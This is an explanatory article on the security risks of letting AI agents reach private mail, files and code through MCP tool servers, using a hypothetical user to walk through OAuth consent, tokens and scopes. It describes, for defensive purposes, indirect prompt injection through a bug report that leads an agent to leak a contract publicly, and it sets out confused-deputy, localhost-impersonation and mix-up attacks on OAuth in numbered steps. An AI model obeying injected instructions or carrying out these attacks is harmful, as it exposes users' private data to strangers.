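# Security risks of giving AI agents access to private data through tool protocols such as MCP

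## How an AI agent reaches private data through a tool server

An AI agent is a language model that chooses and makes tool calls to carry out a user's request. A tool call is a request to another program, called a tool server, to do something the model cannot do by writing text alone, such as searching a mailbox or creating a file. The most widely used standard for connecting agents to tool servers is the Model Context Protocol (MCP), which the AI company Anthropic released in November 2024. A tool server that uses MCP is called an MCP server.

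People use these connections to let an assistant work with their mail, calendars, documents, code and databases. This is both useful and risky because the model can read private material and take actions, and what it does depends partly on text and software from other people.

### The parts a request passes through

Maya, a hypothetical user, has connected an assistant to her mailbox of 40,000 messages, a file store with her contracts and tax records, and the public issue tracker of a small software project she maintains. Anyone can file and read bug reports on the tracker. She asks the assistant how much she owes a supplier named Hartmann and when the payment is due.

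Maya's question goes first to the host application, the program she talks to, which runs the model and holds the connections to the tool servers. The model selects the next step but has no connection of its own to her mail. It can only produce text, including requests for tool calls. The host application passes each request to an MCP client, the part of the application that communicates with a tool server. Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), part of the official specification, pairs every client with a single server, so Maya's host application runs three clients. The client for her mail sends the call to the mail tool server, which queries her mail provider, where the data is held. The answer returns by the same route.

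The tool server and the service behind it can belong to different people, and users may not notice. A mail provider can run its own MCP server, but an unrelated developer can also publish one that logs in to the same provider. For example, *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (Errico, Ngiam and Sojan, 2025) reports that the messaging company Slack had no official MCP server at the time of writing, but the public index of Python packages offered two unofficial ones with official-looking names.

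### One tool call, step by step

The model has to know a tool exists before it can use it, so the client sends the server a `tools/list` request. The server returns each tool's name, a schema for its arguments, and a tool description, which explains to the model what the tool does and how to call it. The host application puts these descriptions in the model's context, which is all the text the model has when it decides what to do next. Maya's mail tool server might offer `search_mail`, `read_message` and `send_message`. The list can change after she has connected the server.

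The model then compares her question with the descriptions, picks `search_mail` and fills in the arguments. The client sends this:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "search_mail",
    "arguments": { "query": "Hartmann invoice", "limit": 2 }
  }
}
```

(A real request also carries a metadata field with the protocol version and the client's capabilities.) The server checks the arguments, translates them into a query that the mail provider understands, and returns what it finds:

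```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "complete",
    "content": [{
      "type": "text",
      "text": "1. From billing@hartmann.example: Invoice 2291, 480 euros, due 30 November.\n2. From jo@example.com: Did you ever pay Hartmann?"
    }],
    "isError": false
  }
}
```

The host application adds the result to the context, and the model either answers Maya or makes another call. One request often leads to several calls. *MCP Usage Surged as the Protocol Went Stateless* (Agentic AI Foundation, 2026) describes a user who asks for help preparing a meeting. The model may check the calendar, look for recent Slack messages and related emails, and open documents in Google Drive. If a call fails because of a bad argument, the client should pass the error message to the model so it can correct and retry the call. A server can also reply with a request for user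 input, such as a missing detail or a confirmation, and the client then repeats the call with the answer attached.

Maya chose none of this. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the page of the specification that covers these messages, describes tools as "model-controlled", meaning that the model can find and call them automatically. It recommends but does not require that a person always be able to refuse a call, and the protocol prescribes no particular way for users to interact with tools. The host application's developer and Maya's settings therefore determine whether she sees a confirmation prompt, which asks her to approve a particular action before the application carries it out.

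The arguments the model chooses affect privacy in two ways. They determine how much private material comes back, since a search for every message from the past year would be as valid as the narrow one above. Whatever the model writes in them also leaves the host application and reaches the operator of the tool server, which is why the specification advises clients to show users the inputs before sending them.

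### Instructions and data in one stream of text

A language model takes one sequence of text as its input. When the model answers Maya, that sequence contains the developer's instructions, the tool descriptions from three servers, Maya's question, and lines from two emails that other people wrote. Host applications put markers around these pieces, and developers train models to give some pieces more authority than others. But the markers are part of the same sequence, and the training makes the model likely, but not certain, to respect those differences in authority. Database programmers can send a command and the user's data separately, so that the database never runs the data as a command, but language models in ordinary use have no equivalent.

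Ordinary email is full of requests, such as "please send the signed copy back" or "use the new address from now on", and users often want an agent to act on them. Training a model to ignore every instruction it finds in an email would therefore not be enough. Errico and colleagues point out that developers generally want agents to react to what they find, look elsewhere when information is missing and try something different after an error, so nobody can predict which tools an agent will call. Because of this flexibility, text written by a stranger can also change what the agent does.

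Prompt injection occurs when a model follows instructions in text that came from someone other than the user or developer. It is indirect when the text arrives in retrieved content, such as an email, a web page or a bug report. By this definition, a hostile instruction that the model reads but does not follow is only an attempted injection.

MCP keeps servers separate, but their outputs mix once they are in the model's context. Under the specification, the host application keeps the full conversation, and each server should receive only the information it needs, with no view into other servers. Maya's issue tracker server cannot query her mailbox, but the model can call both. Maloyan and Namiot (2026) observe in *Breaking the Protocol* that the context combines the outputs of all connected servers without tracking where each came from, so a response from one server can influence a call to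 another. They analysed an early version of the specification, from December 2024, but the 2026 version still relies on the host application to combine material from different servers and enforce the boundaries between them.

Maloyan and Namiot accept that the mixing is useful because it lets an agent read a configuration file through one server and then query a database through another, which full isolation would prevent. But they argue that users should have to agree to such flows explicitly. Maya's assistant, for example, could help her by reading a bug report and finding her earlier correspondence with the person who filed it, but a harmful flow would use the same two connections.

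### Local and remote servers

A tool server can run on the user's computer or on a remote machine, and this affects how it obtains credentials. The client starts a local server as a process on the same computer, and the two exchange messages over the process's standard input and output (stdio). Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) directs such servers to take their credentials from the environment. In practice, that often means a key that the user has pasted into a configuration file, and any other program that can read the file can also use the key. Unless the user confines it, the server also has the same access to the computer as the user's account. Errico and colleagues therefore list the ability to run code on users' machines among the powers of an attacker who publishes a malicious server.

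"Local" describes only where the server runs. A local mail tool server would still fetch Maya's messages from her email provider over the internet, and most host applications would then send the results to a model on the model provider's computers.

A remote server receives calls over HTTP and can use OAuth, a standard under which Maya approves a set of permissions and the client receives an access token. The token is a string that lets its holder make requests within certain limits until it expires or someone revokes it. This is usually better than keeping a key in a file, because Maya can see the permissions she is granting and withdraw them without changing her password. But authorization is optional in MCP, and some operators leave it out. Errico and colleagues cite research by the security company Knostic, which found more than 1,800 MCP servers on the public internet with no authentication.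 That count dates from 2025 or earlier, when MCP was far less widespread.

### History and use

According to *Two Years of MCP Builders* (Soria Parra and Delimarsky, 2026), Soria Parra approached Justin Spahr-Summers in the summer of 2024 with a proposal for an open protocol to connect AI applications to tools and data, and the two built it over the next few months. Anthropic published it on 25 November 2024. Until then, every new data source had needed its own custom connection, according to Anthropic's *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* (2024).

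At first, the protocol was used mainly with local servers. On launch day, the software developer Simon Willison (2024) described connections to external servers over HTTP, which the specification already set out, as the next step. The March 2025 revision brought remote servers and authorization, which made it much easier for non-programmers to connect an assistant to a company's service. In December 2025, the project moved to the Agentic AI Foundation, which is under the Linux Foundation.

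The current revision of the protocol, dated 2026-07-28, is the largest since the launch. Previously, a client calling a remote server opened with a handshake, and the server could issue a session identifier that the client had to attach to every later request. An operator with many machines had to either route each client back to the machine that held its session or share the session records among all of them. Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) records the removal of both the handshake and the session. Each request now carries the information needed to process it, so any machine can answer. A server that has to keep information between calls gives the model an identifier to pass back, and that identifier could leak. The revision does not separate instructions from data in the model's context.

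Use of MCP has grown quickly, though the available figures measure it only indirectly. Soria Parra and Delimarsky, who both lead the project, report more than 700 million downloads of MCP's software development kits in the 30 days to 23 November 2026, up from more than 90 million in November 2025. They put the total since launch at 5 billion. Downloads are a poor measure of how many people use MCP, because automated systems fetch the same package many times. The Agentic AI Foundation reports that tool calls from ChatGPT users reached 98 times their January level by August 2026, but gives no absolute number.

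Anthropic's own counts are closer to what users see. Its *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) says the directory for its assistant Claude had over 950 MCP servers in July, with millions of daily users. By November, the company claimed more than 10,000 connectors for Claude, according to Diario TI's *Los servidores MCP ya pueden entregar a Claude instrucciones de uso propias*, which cautions that nobody has independently verified the figure. The two counts may cover different things.

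AgentMarketIndex's online catalogue, *MCP servers ranked by measured installs*, listed 78,140 MCP servers in early December 2026, with installation counts for fewer than a third of them. Ten listings accounted for about three quarters of the installations among the top 200. These figures deserve some caution, but if they are roughly right, a few packages account for most use of installable servers, and there are a very large number of other servers that few people have examined.

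### Three sources of harm

An attack through outside text requires the least access. Anyone who knows Maya's address can email her, and any visitor can file a bug report, without a password or access to the host application. If the model follows instructions in that text, it acts with Maya's permissions. The issue tracker is a particular problem because strangers can read it as well as write to it, so the agent can expose a private email by quoting it in a public comment.

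A malicious server or a stolen token can expose private data even if the model does nothing wrong. A dishonest operator of the mail tool server, or an intruder on the operator's machines, can copy every query and result that passes through the server. A malicious server can also place instructions for the model in its tool descriptions and results. Someone who steals an access token can bypass the agent and make any request the token allows while it remains valid.

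The model can disclose private data by mistake, without an attacker. Maya might ask for a reply to a bug report, and the model might paste in a customer's email, including their name and phone number, because the email answers the question. Errico and colleagues call such an agent an "inadvertent adversary". Each call is well formed and within the agent's permissions, but the combination discloses something it should not. Their other examples include exposing passwords or keys while debugging, and looking for another route after a control has blocked the first. All three work for security and compliance companies, which have an interest in the subject, but the category does not depend on their products. The usual defences against attackers miss these mistakes. Maya could vet every server and filter every incoming message, and the model could still post the wrong email. Tighter permissions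 would help against both mistakes and attackers, since the model cannot disclose a message it cannot read.

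## How a user grants access with OAuth

When Maya connects a remote server, she sets the first limit on what the model can read. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) bases this step on a subset of OAuth 2.1. An authorization server prompts her for consent and issues the access tokens. The MCP server's operator can run the authorization server too, or have another company run it.

Authorization is optional in MCP, but a server that uses it and takes calls over HTTP SHOULD follow the OAuth flow. The specification uses MUST for requirements and SHOULD for recommendations, so an operator who hands out fixed keys instead goes against a recommendation but does not violate a requirement. Local stdio servers SHOULD NOT use the flow.

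Duende Software (2026) counts six changes to authorization in the July 2026 revision. Anthropic was still rolling out support for the revision across the Claude products on the day it was released, so a connection may still follow some of the older rules.

### Maya's first connection

Suppose the company behind Maya's file store runs its own MCP server, and her host application is a program on her laptop. She gives the program the server's address. The client sends its first request without a token, and the server refuses it:

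```http
HTTP/1.1 401 Unauthorized
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer resource_metadata="https://mcp.filestore.example/.well-known/oauth-protected-resource",
                         scope="files:read"
```

The first value in the header is the address of a short document about the server. The second is the scope, or named permission, that the request needs. If the header omits the document's address, the client looks for the document at standard locations on the same server.

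The document lists at least one authorization server, in this case `https://login.filestore.example`. The client downloads that server's metadata, which gives the addresses of its consent page and its token endpoint (where clients collect tokens), the features it supports, and an identifier called the issuer. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Server Discovery* (2026) requires the issuer in the metadata to be identical to the one the client used to look it up. If an attacker's site serves metadata that names the file store as issuer, the client has to discard it.

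During discovery, the client follows addresses from a server that may be hostile. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* warns that a malicious server can point the client at machines inside a private network. A client running in a company's data centre might then fetch cloud credentials from an internal service and reveal part of the reply in an error message. The guidance recommends that clients require HTTPS, block private network addresses and apply the same checks to redirects. Clients must also reject an authorization address that is really a script, and they must not use a command shell to open authorization addresses.

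Before opening the browser, the client generates a random secret called a code verifier and computes a code challenge from it:

challenge = BASE64URL(SHA-256(verifier))

SHA-256 is a one-way function, so nobody can work back from the challenge to the verifier. This technique is called PKCE (Proof Key for Code Exchange). The client then opens Maya's browser at the authorization server with a request like this one, which appears here without its web encoding and with shortened random values:

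```text
https://login.filestore.example/authorize
  ?response_type=code
  &client_id=https://assistant.example/client.json
  &redirect_uri=http://localhost:3000/callback
  &scope=files:read
  &resource=https://mcp.filestore.example
  &code_challenge=Xk3v...
  &code_challenge_method=S256
  &state=9f2c...
```

Maya signs in on the file store's own page, so the assistant never handles her password. A consent screen then shows her the client's name and the access it requests. This is the only step where she makes a decision, and the MCP specification leaves most of the screen's design to the operator of the authorization server.

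If she approves, the authorization server sends her browser back to the callback address (`redirect_uri`) with an authorization code, a short-lived string that the client can exchange for a token. The response should also include the authorization server's issuer identifier in the `iss` parameter, and the client compares it with the one it recorded before opening the browser.

The client now sends the code, the verifier and the `resource` value to the token endpoint. The authorization server hashes the verifier, compares the result with the challenge it received earlier, and returns an access token. It may add a refresh token, which the client can use to get further access tokens without involving Maya. The client then repeats its original request with the token attached:

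```http
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Host: mcp.filestore.example
Authorization: Bearer eyJhbGciOi...
```

Every later request must also include this header. The client must not put the token in the web address, because servers and proxies commonly log addresses. The MCP server checks the token and answers. Maya does not need to do anything more for OAuth until the access expires, she revokes it, or an operation needs a scope she has not granted.

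### What the checks on the code and token prevent

The authorization code passes through the browser, where other software may be able to see it. PKCE protects the code because anyone who intercepts it also needs the verifier to exchange it, and the verifier has not yet left the client. The exchange also fails if someone substitutes a code from a different login. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) requires clients to stop if the authorization server's metadata does not list PKCE support. But PKCE shows only that the program exchanging the code is the one that started the flow, so it does not stop an attacker who started the flow and has a valid verifier.

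Two further checks protect the callback. The authorization server must accept only a callback address that exactly matches a registered one, so that an attacker cannot have the code sent to another website. The client should also put a random `state` value in the request and discard any response that does not contain the same value.

Once the client has a token, the `resource` parameter and audience validation keep it from being used at a server it wasn't issued for. One authorization server may issue tokens for several services. Suppose the file store shares an authorization server with a photo-printing service, and Maya connects an MCP server for each. If a token for the printing service also worked at the file store, a dishonest operator of the printing server could use it to read her contracts. To prevent this, the client names the intended server in `resource`, the authorization server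 records it as the token's audience, and each MCP server rejects any token with a different audience.

This protection depends on the client, the authorization server and the MCP server. Clients must send `resource` even to an authorization server that ignores it, but the specification states that the binding works only where the authorization server supports it. An MCP server that skips the audience check may accept tokens meant for other services, even if Maya's client did everything correctly.

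### How the client identifies itself

The consent screen helps Maya only if the name on it belongs to the program that will receive the token. In MCP, that program is often new to the authorization server. *Enable URL-based Client Registration using OAuth Client ID Metadata Documents* (Carleton and Parecki, 2025) describes the typical case, in which a user finds a server and wants to connect a client to it, but the client's developer and the server's operator have never heard of each other.

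If the client and server have an existing relationship, the developer can register the client in advance and receive a client ID, which the client should then use. But a developer cannot register with servers that do not exist when the program ships, and users who are asked to register the client themselves must manage its credentials.

MCP's earlier solution was Dynamic Client Registration, in which the client sends its name and callback addresses to the authorization server and immediately receives a new client ID. The server has to trust these details, so a malicious program can register under the name of a well-known assistant with its own callback address. The server's operator also has to store a growing number of registrations and decide when to delete old ones.

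The July 2026 revision deprecates this method in favour of Client ID Metadata Documents. Under the new method, the client ID is itself an HTTPS address, where the client's developer publishes a small file:

```json
{
  "client_id": "https://assistant.example/client.json",
  "client_name": "Example Assistant",
  "redirect_uris": ["http://localhost:3000/callback"]
}
```

The authorization server fetches the file, confirms that the `client_id` in it exactly matches the file's address, and checks that the requested callback is on the file's list. An attacker who does not control `assistant.example` cannot add a website to that list. The server's operator can accept clients from any domain, restrict access to domains it trusts, or treat new domains with more suspicion. The same ID works at every authorization server that supports the method.

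The new method requires every developer to have a website, even for a program that runs entirely on the desktop. It also requires authorization servers to fetch addresses that strangers supply, which exposes them to the private-network attack described above. The underlying standard, *OAuth Client ID Metadata Document* (Parecki and Smith, 2026), is unfinished. A new draft was published on 6 July, but the MCP specification still refers to an earlier one. The old method will remain in use for some time, because *Client Registration* (Model Context Protocol, 2026) lets clients fall back to it when an authorization server does not support metadata documents.

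Metadata documents do not solve the problem of identifying programs on the user's own computer. A desktop program usually receives the authorization code by listening on a numbered port at a `localhost` address, which always refers to the computer the browser is running on. Any program on that computer can listen on a free port. A malicious program on Maya's laptop could use this as follows:

1. It starts an authorization flow and gives the real assistant's metadata address as its client ID.
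2. It listens on a `localhost` port and gives that as the callback address.
3. The authorization server fetches the real metadata document, finds nothing wrong with it, and shows Maya the real assistant's name.
4. Maya approves, and her browser delivers the code to the malicious program.

The metadata document proves that someone controls a domain, but it does not identify the program listening on Maya's laptop. PKCE does not stop the attack, because the malicious program generated the verifier. Carleton and Parecki note that Dynamic Client Registration has the same weakness, so the change does not make the problem worse.

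Authorization servers must show the host name of the callback address and should add a warning if a client uses only `localhost`. These measures are fairly weak because the host name is the same for the real assistant and the impostor. Maya's best clue may be that she had not just tried to connect anything. Carleton and Parecki suggest that Apple's and Google's app verification services could help, but these are not available on every platform. Alternatively, the client's developer could run a service that signs short-lived proofs of identity, though an attacker might relay requests to it.

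The attack requires malicious software on Maya's computer. Such software could already read her local files, but the attack also gives it access to data she stores elsewhere, under a name that she and the file store trust.

### How a proxy server can give an attacker access

Maya's mail setup is more complicated because the developer of her mail tool server has no connection with her mail provider, and the server reaches her mailbox through the provider's public interface. Tabata (2026) notes in *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* that MCP authorization can span several systems and organizations in this way. The mail server is a proxy that issues MCP clients tokens for access to itself and is also an OAuth client of the mail provider. Connecting it therefore involves two authorization codes and two access tokens.

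Many providers do not let clients register automatically, so the developer registered the proxy once by hand. It uses the same fixed client ID with the provider for every user and every MCP client, and the provider cannot tell which program is behind a request. Combined with automatic registration at the proxy and a cookie that remembers consent, this allows the following attack:

1. Maya connects her assistant in the normal way. The mail provider asks whether the proxy may read her mail, she approves, and the provider stores a cookie in her browser so that it does not have to ask again for this client ID.
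2. The attacker uses Dynamic Client Registration to register a client with the proxy, giving a callback address on the attacker's own website.
3. The attacker sends Maya a link that starts an authorization request for that client, and she clicks it.
4. Her browser reaches the mail provider with the proxy's fixed client ID. The provider finds the cookie and skips the consent screen.
5. The provider sends its code to the proxy, which exchanges it for a token to Maya's mailbox.
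6. The proxy creates its own code for the attacker's client and sends Maya's browser to the attacker's website with it.
7. The attacker exchanges this code for a token to the proxy and can now use the proxy to read Maya's mail.

The proxy is a confused deputy, a program that someone tricks into using its legitimate authority on their behalf. Maya clicked one link and was not asked to approve anything. PKCE does not prevent this because the attacker's client started the flow, and the audience check passes because the stolen access is for the proxy.

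To counter this, the proxy must ask for the user's consent itself before sending them to the mail provider. It must record which clients each user has approved and, for any other client, show a page with the client's name, the permissions it requests from the provider and the callback address. Maya would then see that a program she does not recognize is requesting permission to read her mail and that the result would go to an unknown website.

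This page protects Maya only if an attacker cannot bypass it. If the proxy stores consent in a cookie, the cookie must be tied to one client, since a general record that she has consented would recreate the original flaw. Other websites must not be able to embed the page in an invisible frame and trick her into clicking the button. The proxy must also store the `state` value that it will check when the provider responds only after she approves. Otherwise, an attacker can construct a request that skips the page.

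The attack still works on proxies that support Dynamic Client Registration, even though it is deprecated. The guidance does not list metadata documents among the conditions for the attack, but an attacker can publish one on their own domain. A proxy that accepted documents from any domain without asking for consent to each client would probably be vulnerable in much the same way.

### Why a server must not pass tokens along

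The MCP specification forbids token passthrough, in which the client supplies a token for the mail provider and the proxy forwards it unchanged with each request. A proxy's developer might prefer this because it is simpler than managing two tokens.

With token passthrough, the proxy accepts a token that was not issued for it, so an attacker who has stolen a token from Maya's calendar program could use it at the proxy if it also covers mail. The proxy then forwards the token to the provider, which may wrongly assume that the proxy has checked it. Limits on the number of requests may stop working, as may monitoring that depends on knowing which program is calling. The provider's logs may also show the requests under an identity other than the proxy's, which makes the cause of a problem harder to find.

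As a countermeasure, the proxy must accept only tokens issued for it and use a separate token, issued by the provider's authorization server, to contact the provider. Model Context Protocol advises this even for a server that only forwards requests today, because the developer may later want to add security controls. But the operator then holds tokens to many people's mailboxes, which makes its storage a valuable target.

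### How a client can send a code to the wrong server

A client that connects to many MCP servers will also interact with many authorization servers, and an attacker may control one of them. In a mix-up attack, the attacker tricks the client into sending the attacker an authorization code that a legitimate authorization server issued.

Suppose Maya tries a new MCP server run by an attacker. Its metadata points to the attacker's authorization server, so her assistant records that server as the issuer and opens her browser there. The attacker redirects the browser to the file store's authorization server and copies her assistant's client ID, callback address and code challenge into the new request. Maya sees her file store's familiar approval page, which names her own assistant, and she approves. The file store then sends the authorization code to her assistant.

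The client still treats the code as coming from the attacker's authorization server, so it sends the code and the PKCE verifier to the attacker's token endpoint. The attacker uses both to get a token from the file store. PKCE does not prevent this because the client itself discloses the verifier. The `resource` parameter does not help either, since the attacker can change it while redirecting the browser.

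The `iss` parameter lets the client detect the switch. The file store's response contains the file store's issuer, but the client recorded the attacker's. The client must compare the two character by character and, because they do not match, reject the response before it sends the code anywhere. The attacker also cannot get the client to record the file store as the issuer, because the client rejects metadata whose issuer does not match where it came from.

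The client makes this comparison whenever a response includes `iss`, even if the metadata it has on record does not list support for `iss`. In a mix-up attack, the attacker wrote that metadata and would have no reason to list support. If the metadata lists support but the response lacks `iss`, the client must reject the response. If the metadata does not list support and the response lacks `iss`, the client continues, and the attack can succeed.

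Maya's protection therefore depends on whether her file store sends `iss`. According to the current specification, authorization servers SHOULD send it, and a later revision is expected to require it. Until then, even an up-to-date client remains exposed to a mix-up attack involving an honest authorization server that omits `iss`.

### When an employer gives consent instead

In the flow so far, Maya decides which servers her assistant may use, but companies often want to decide this for their employees. The Enterprise-Managed Authorization extension moves the decision to the company's identity provider, the service that employees already use to sign in to their work accounts. Carleton (2026) announced in *Enterprise-Managed Authorization* on 18 June that the extension was stable.

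If Maya's employer used it, she would sign in to the host application with her work account, and the client would keep proof of her identity. To reach an MCP server, the client would send this proof to the identity provider, which would check the company's rules about her role, her groups and the conditions of access. If the rules allowed it, the identity provider would return a short-lived signed grant, which Model Context Protocol's *Identity assertion* describes as a statement that a given user may reach a given MCP server through a given client. The client would exchange the grant for an access token at the MCP server's authorization server. Maya would not see a consent screen for that server.

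An employee would find the tools she needs already connected the first time she logged in. The company can also require a connector to go through its identity provider, which would stop her from accidentally linking a personal account to a work tool. If she changed department, her access could change with her role. The Agentic AI Foundation lists this as one of the main uses of the extension, along with managing access when employees are hired, promoted or leave.

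But Maya would no longer see the screen showing which program was requesting which data, or have the chance to refuse when it connected. Carleton treats the missing screen as a saving in effort, and for most work tools it is. But a work mailbox can contain messages about an employee's health or a dispute with a manager. Maya could leave that mailbox disconnected under the standard flow, whereas the extension would let an administrator connect it before she first opened the assistant. Whether she could then disconnect it would depend on the host application and company policy. Central sign-in also means that an intruder who took over her work account could reach every server the company had approved for her.

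Withdrawing access is easier with a central service, though perhaps not as fast as the documentation suggests. According to Model Context Protocol's *Enterprise-Managed Authorization*, revoking an employee's access takes effect immediately in all clients. The identity provider can immediately stop issuing new grants, but an access token that a client already holds may work until it expires. Anthropic's *Centrally manage authorization for MCP connectors* makes the more modest claim that administrators can shorten token lifetimes so that a former employee's access "expires fast". Short lifetimes are practical here because the client can get a new token without interrupting the user.

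The extension is optional, and clients do not enable it by default. Okta was the only supported identity provider at launch. Anthropic offered the feature as a beta for Claude's Team and Enterprise plans, and seven companies, including Asana, Atlassian and Figma, supported it on their servers.

### What a valid token does not show

Each of these checks concerns a program or a credential. Together they can show that Maya or her employer allowed this client to call this server within certain limits, but not why the client is making a particular call.

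Suppose Maya has connected her file store correctly and asks the assistant to summarize new bug reports. One report contains an instruction to open her latest contract and quote it in a public comment, and the model follows it. The client calls the file server with a valid token that has the right audience and the `files:read` scope. The server correctly returns the contract, because Maya allowed the assistant to read her files. The call that posts the comment to the issue tracker passes the same checks. Neither server receives any information about whether Maya or the bug report prompted the request.

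Security companies have made this point about the July 2026 revision. Tigera's *MCP’s Auth Hardening* welcomes the six changes but notes that they cover how a client authenticates to a server, and that the specification does not cover the authorization of individual requests. *MCP Auth vs Tool-Call Authorization After the 2026-07-28 Spec*, published by the authorization company Permit.io, argues that deciding whether to allow an action requires policy checks beyond OAuth scopes. Both companies have a commercial interest in selling additional controls, but the OAuth flow supports their point.

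A policy check on each call could refuse all access to the contracts folder, or require Maya's approval before anything appears in a public comment. But if the check receives only the tool's name and arguments, it cannot distinguish a request Maya made from one that came from the bug report. Only the host application holds both the text the model read and the call it produced, and OAuth does not require it to track how the two are connected.

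## How much read access an agent should have

An MCP server cannot distinguish a call prompted by Maya from one prompted by a stranger's bug report, so the harm a wrong call can do depends on what the token allows. If the token covers one folder, a tricked or mistaken model can expose that folder but nothing else in the file store. Under the principle of least privilege, a program should hold only the permissions its task requires. This is hard to apply to agents because the client requests permissions when Maya connects a server, often before anyone knows what the tasks will be.

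### How the client chooses its first scopes

Model Context Protocol gives clients an order in which to look for scopes. Written as an algorithm, it is:

```text
if the 401 response names scopes:
    request those scopes
else if the server's metadata has a scopes_supported list:
    request every scope on the list
else:
    leave out the scope parameter
```

When Maya connected her file store, the 401 response listed `files:read`, so the client requested only that scope. Servers SHOULD list scopes in this response but do not have to. If a server gives no guidance on scopes at all, the authorization server applies its own default, which may be narrow or broad.

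If the client falls back on `scopes_supported`, Maya's access depends on which scopes the server's operator listed there. The specification intends the field to hold only the minimal scopes for basic functions, but its name suggests a list of every scope the server supports, and an operator could easily fill it that way. In its security guidance, Model Context Protocol lists this as a common mistake and describes how the client then requests every listed scope and receives a token with scopes such as `files:*`, `db:*` and `admin:*`. An attacker who finds the token in a log can use it on tools unrelated to the user's task.

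The same guidance nevertheless defends the fallback on the grounds that a general-purpose client lacks the information to choose among a particular service's scopes. By this reasoning, the client should request them all and let the authorization server and the user determine the right ones at the consent screen. Model Context Protocol describes this as "following the principle of least privilege".

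Suppose Maya wants her assistant to find one contract, which requires only `files:read`. Her file store lists `files:read`, `files:write`, `files:share` and `files:delete`, but its 401 response doesn't specify any scopes, so the client requests all four. The authorization server could issue a token for `files:read` alone, or the consent screen could let her untick the other three. MCP allows both but doesn't require either. If the screen offers only "Allow" and "Cancel", she has to accept all four scopes or do without the assistant.

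The claim therefore holds only if the server's list is already minimal or someone narrows the request afterwards. Tick boxes would help less than they seem to, because Maya would have to work out whether a search needs `files:share`. The operator is much better placed to decide this, and can do so by naming `files:read` in the 401 response.

### How step-up authorization adds scopes

Suppose the file store starts with `files:read`, and Maya later asks the assistant to save a summary next to the contract. The server refuses the call with a 403 response containing the error `insufficient_scope` and the required scope, `files:write`.

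This refusal starts step-up authorization, in which the client asks for a further scope only when an operation first needs it. If R is the set of scopes the client has requested so far and C is the set named in the refusal, the client's next request is their union:

R_new = R ∪ C

The client sends Maya back to the authorization server with this request and retries the call with the new token. It should stop after a few failed attempts.

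In *MCP Scope Step-Up Authorization*, Soormally explains why a client needs to request the union of its existing and new scopes. His company, WunderGraph, had built an MCP server that required `employees:read` to look up employees and `employees:write` to change their records. When the server refused a request for lack of `employees:write`, the official TypeScript client requested only that scope, and the new token no longer allowed reads. The server then refused the next read for lack of `employees:read`, the client again requested only the missing scope, and the browser kept opening new authorization pages.

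At the time, the specification called for servers to repeat the client's existing scopes in each refusal. Soormally objected that this forced servers to track information the client already had. He proposed that servers list only the scopes the current operation needs and that clients track the scopes they have accumulated, which is how the July 2026 revision works.

The union rule ends the loop, but it only ever adds scopes. Maya's token might grow like this over two weeks:

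| Day | What Maya asks for | Scope in the refusal | Scopes on the token afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Find a contract | `files:read` | `files:read` |
| 3 | Save a summary of it | `files:write` | `files:read`, `files:write` |
| 8 | Send her accountant a link | `files:share` | `files:read`, `files:write`, `files:share` |
| 12 | Find another contract | None | `files:read`, `files:write`, `files:share` |

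On day 12, the assistant does the same kind of work as on day 1, but its token now lets it overwrite Maya's files and share them with strangers. She approved every addition, and each was reasonable at the time. But with step-up, she approves each scope once, not each time the assistant uses it. WorkOS, which sells login and authorization software, likewise points out that a `files:write` grant a user made an hour ago is still in effect.

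A client may ask Maya again for a scope she has refused. The union defined in the specification includes all the scopes the client previously requested, even any she did not grant. If she declined `files:share` on day 8, a client that followed this rule literally would include it on the next consent screen, even for an unrelated operation. However, under the security guidance, clients should remember recent failures so they do not keep asking for a scope the user has denied.

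The step-up flow never removes a scope. Expiry limits how long a stolen access token works, but a client with a refresh token can get a new access token with the same scopes. Maya can revoke the grant and reconnect. If the client has discarded its record, it then starts again from the 401 response. However, few people will remember to do this.

OAuth offers a better option, though MCP does not require it. A client can request fewer scopes when it uses a refresh token, and the refresh token keeps all of its original scopes. Maya's host application could therefore use a read-only access token for searches and get a wider one when she asks for a change, without another consent screen. An attacker who stole the read-only token could not use it to alter her files. To stop a tricked model from altering them as well, the host application would have to check with Maya before switching to the wider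 token.

Permissions also accumulate as software changes. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, describes servers that request additional scopes for new features but keep their existing scopes when developers remove old features. It also points out that an attacker who manipulates an agent gains the combined abilities of every tool connected to it.

### Why scopes are coarser than tasks

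A provider defines its scopes in advance, for all users and every program that might connect. A scope can separate reading mail from sending it, but Maya's task selects messages by their content, and the provider could not have created a scope for "messages that show what I owe Hartmann" before she asked. OAuth's Rich Authorization Requests extension lets the client describe the permission it wants, such as access to one account, in a structured form, but the extension is not among the standards MCP uses for authorization.

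Gmail's `gmail.readonly` scope lets a program read every message and attachment in the mailbox. The narrower `gmail.metadata` scope covers labels and headers, including senders and subject lines, but not message text. Under that scope, Maya's assistant could see that Hartmann had written but probably not how much she owed. It also could not use Gmail's search, so it would have to page through the headers. Neither scope can be limited to one sender, label or period.

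The difference between headers and message text matters especially for Maya's other accounts. Many services send password-reset links and login codes by email, so even read-only access to the text of her messages may let someone take over those accounts.

Google Drive lets a user limit a program's access to individual files. The `drive.readonly` scope covers everything in the drive, while `drive.file` covers only files that the program created or that the user opened with it, usually through Google's file picker. But `drive.file` also lets the program edit those files, so Maya would have to grant write access to limit which files it can read. She would also need to know which file to pick, which works well for "summarize this contract" but badly for "find the contract that mentions late fees".

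On GitHub, the type of credential determines how narrowly a user can limit an agent's access. The older OAuth scope `repo` gives a program read and write access to every private repository the user can reach, and has no read-only version. With a fine-grained personal access token or a GitHub App, Maya can select repositories and grant read-only access to their code. She could grant access only to the repository that has her public issue tracker, which would block attacks that use a bug report to make an agent read code in her private repositories.

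A tool server that acts as a proxy, as Maya's mail server does, can hold a broader token than hers. Her token might carry the scope `mail:search`, while the server's carries `gmail.readonly`. The narrower scope limits what the agent can request, but the server's operator can still read the whole mailbox.

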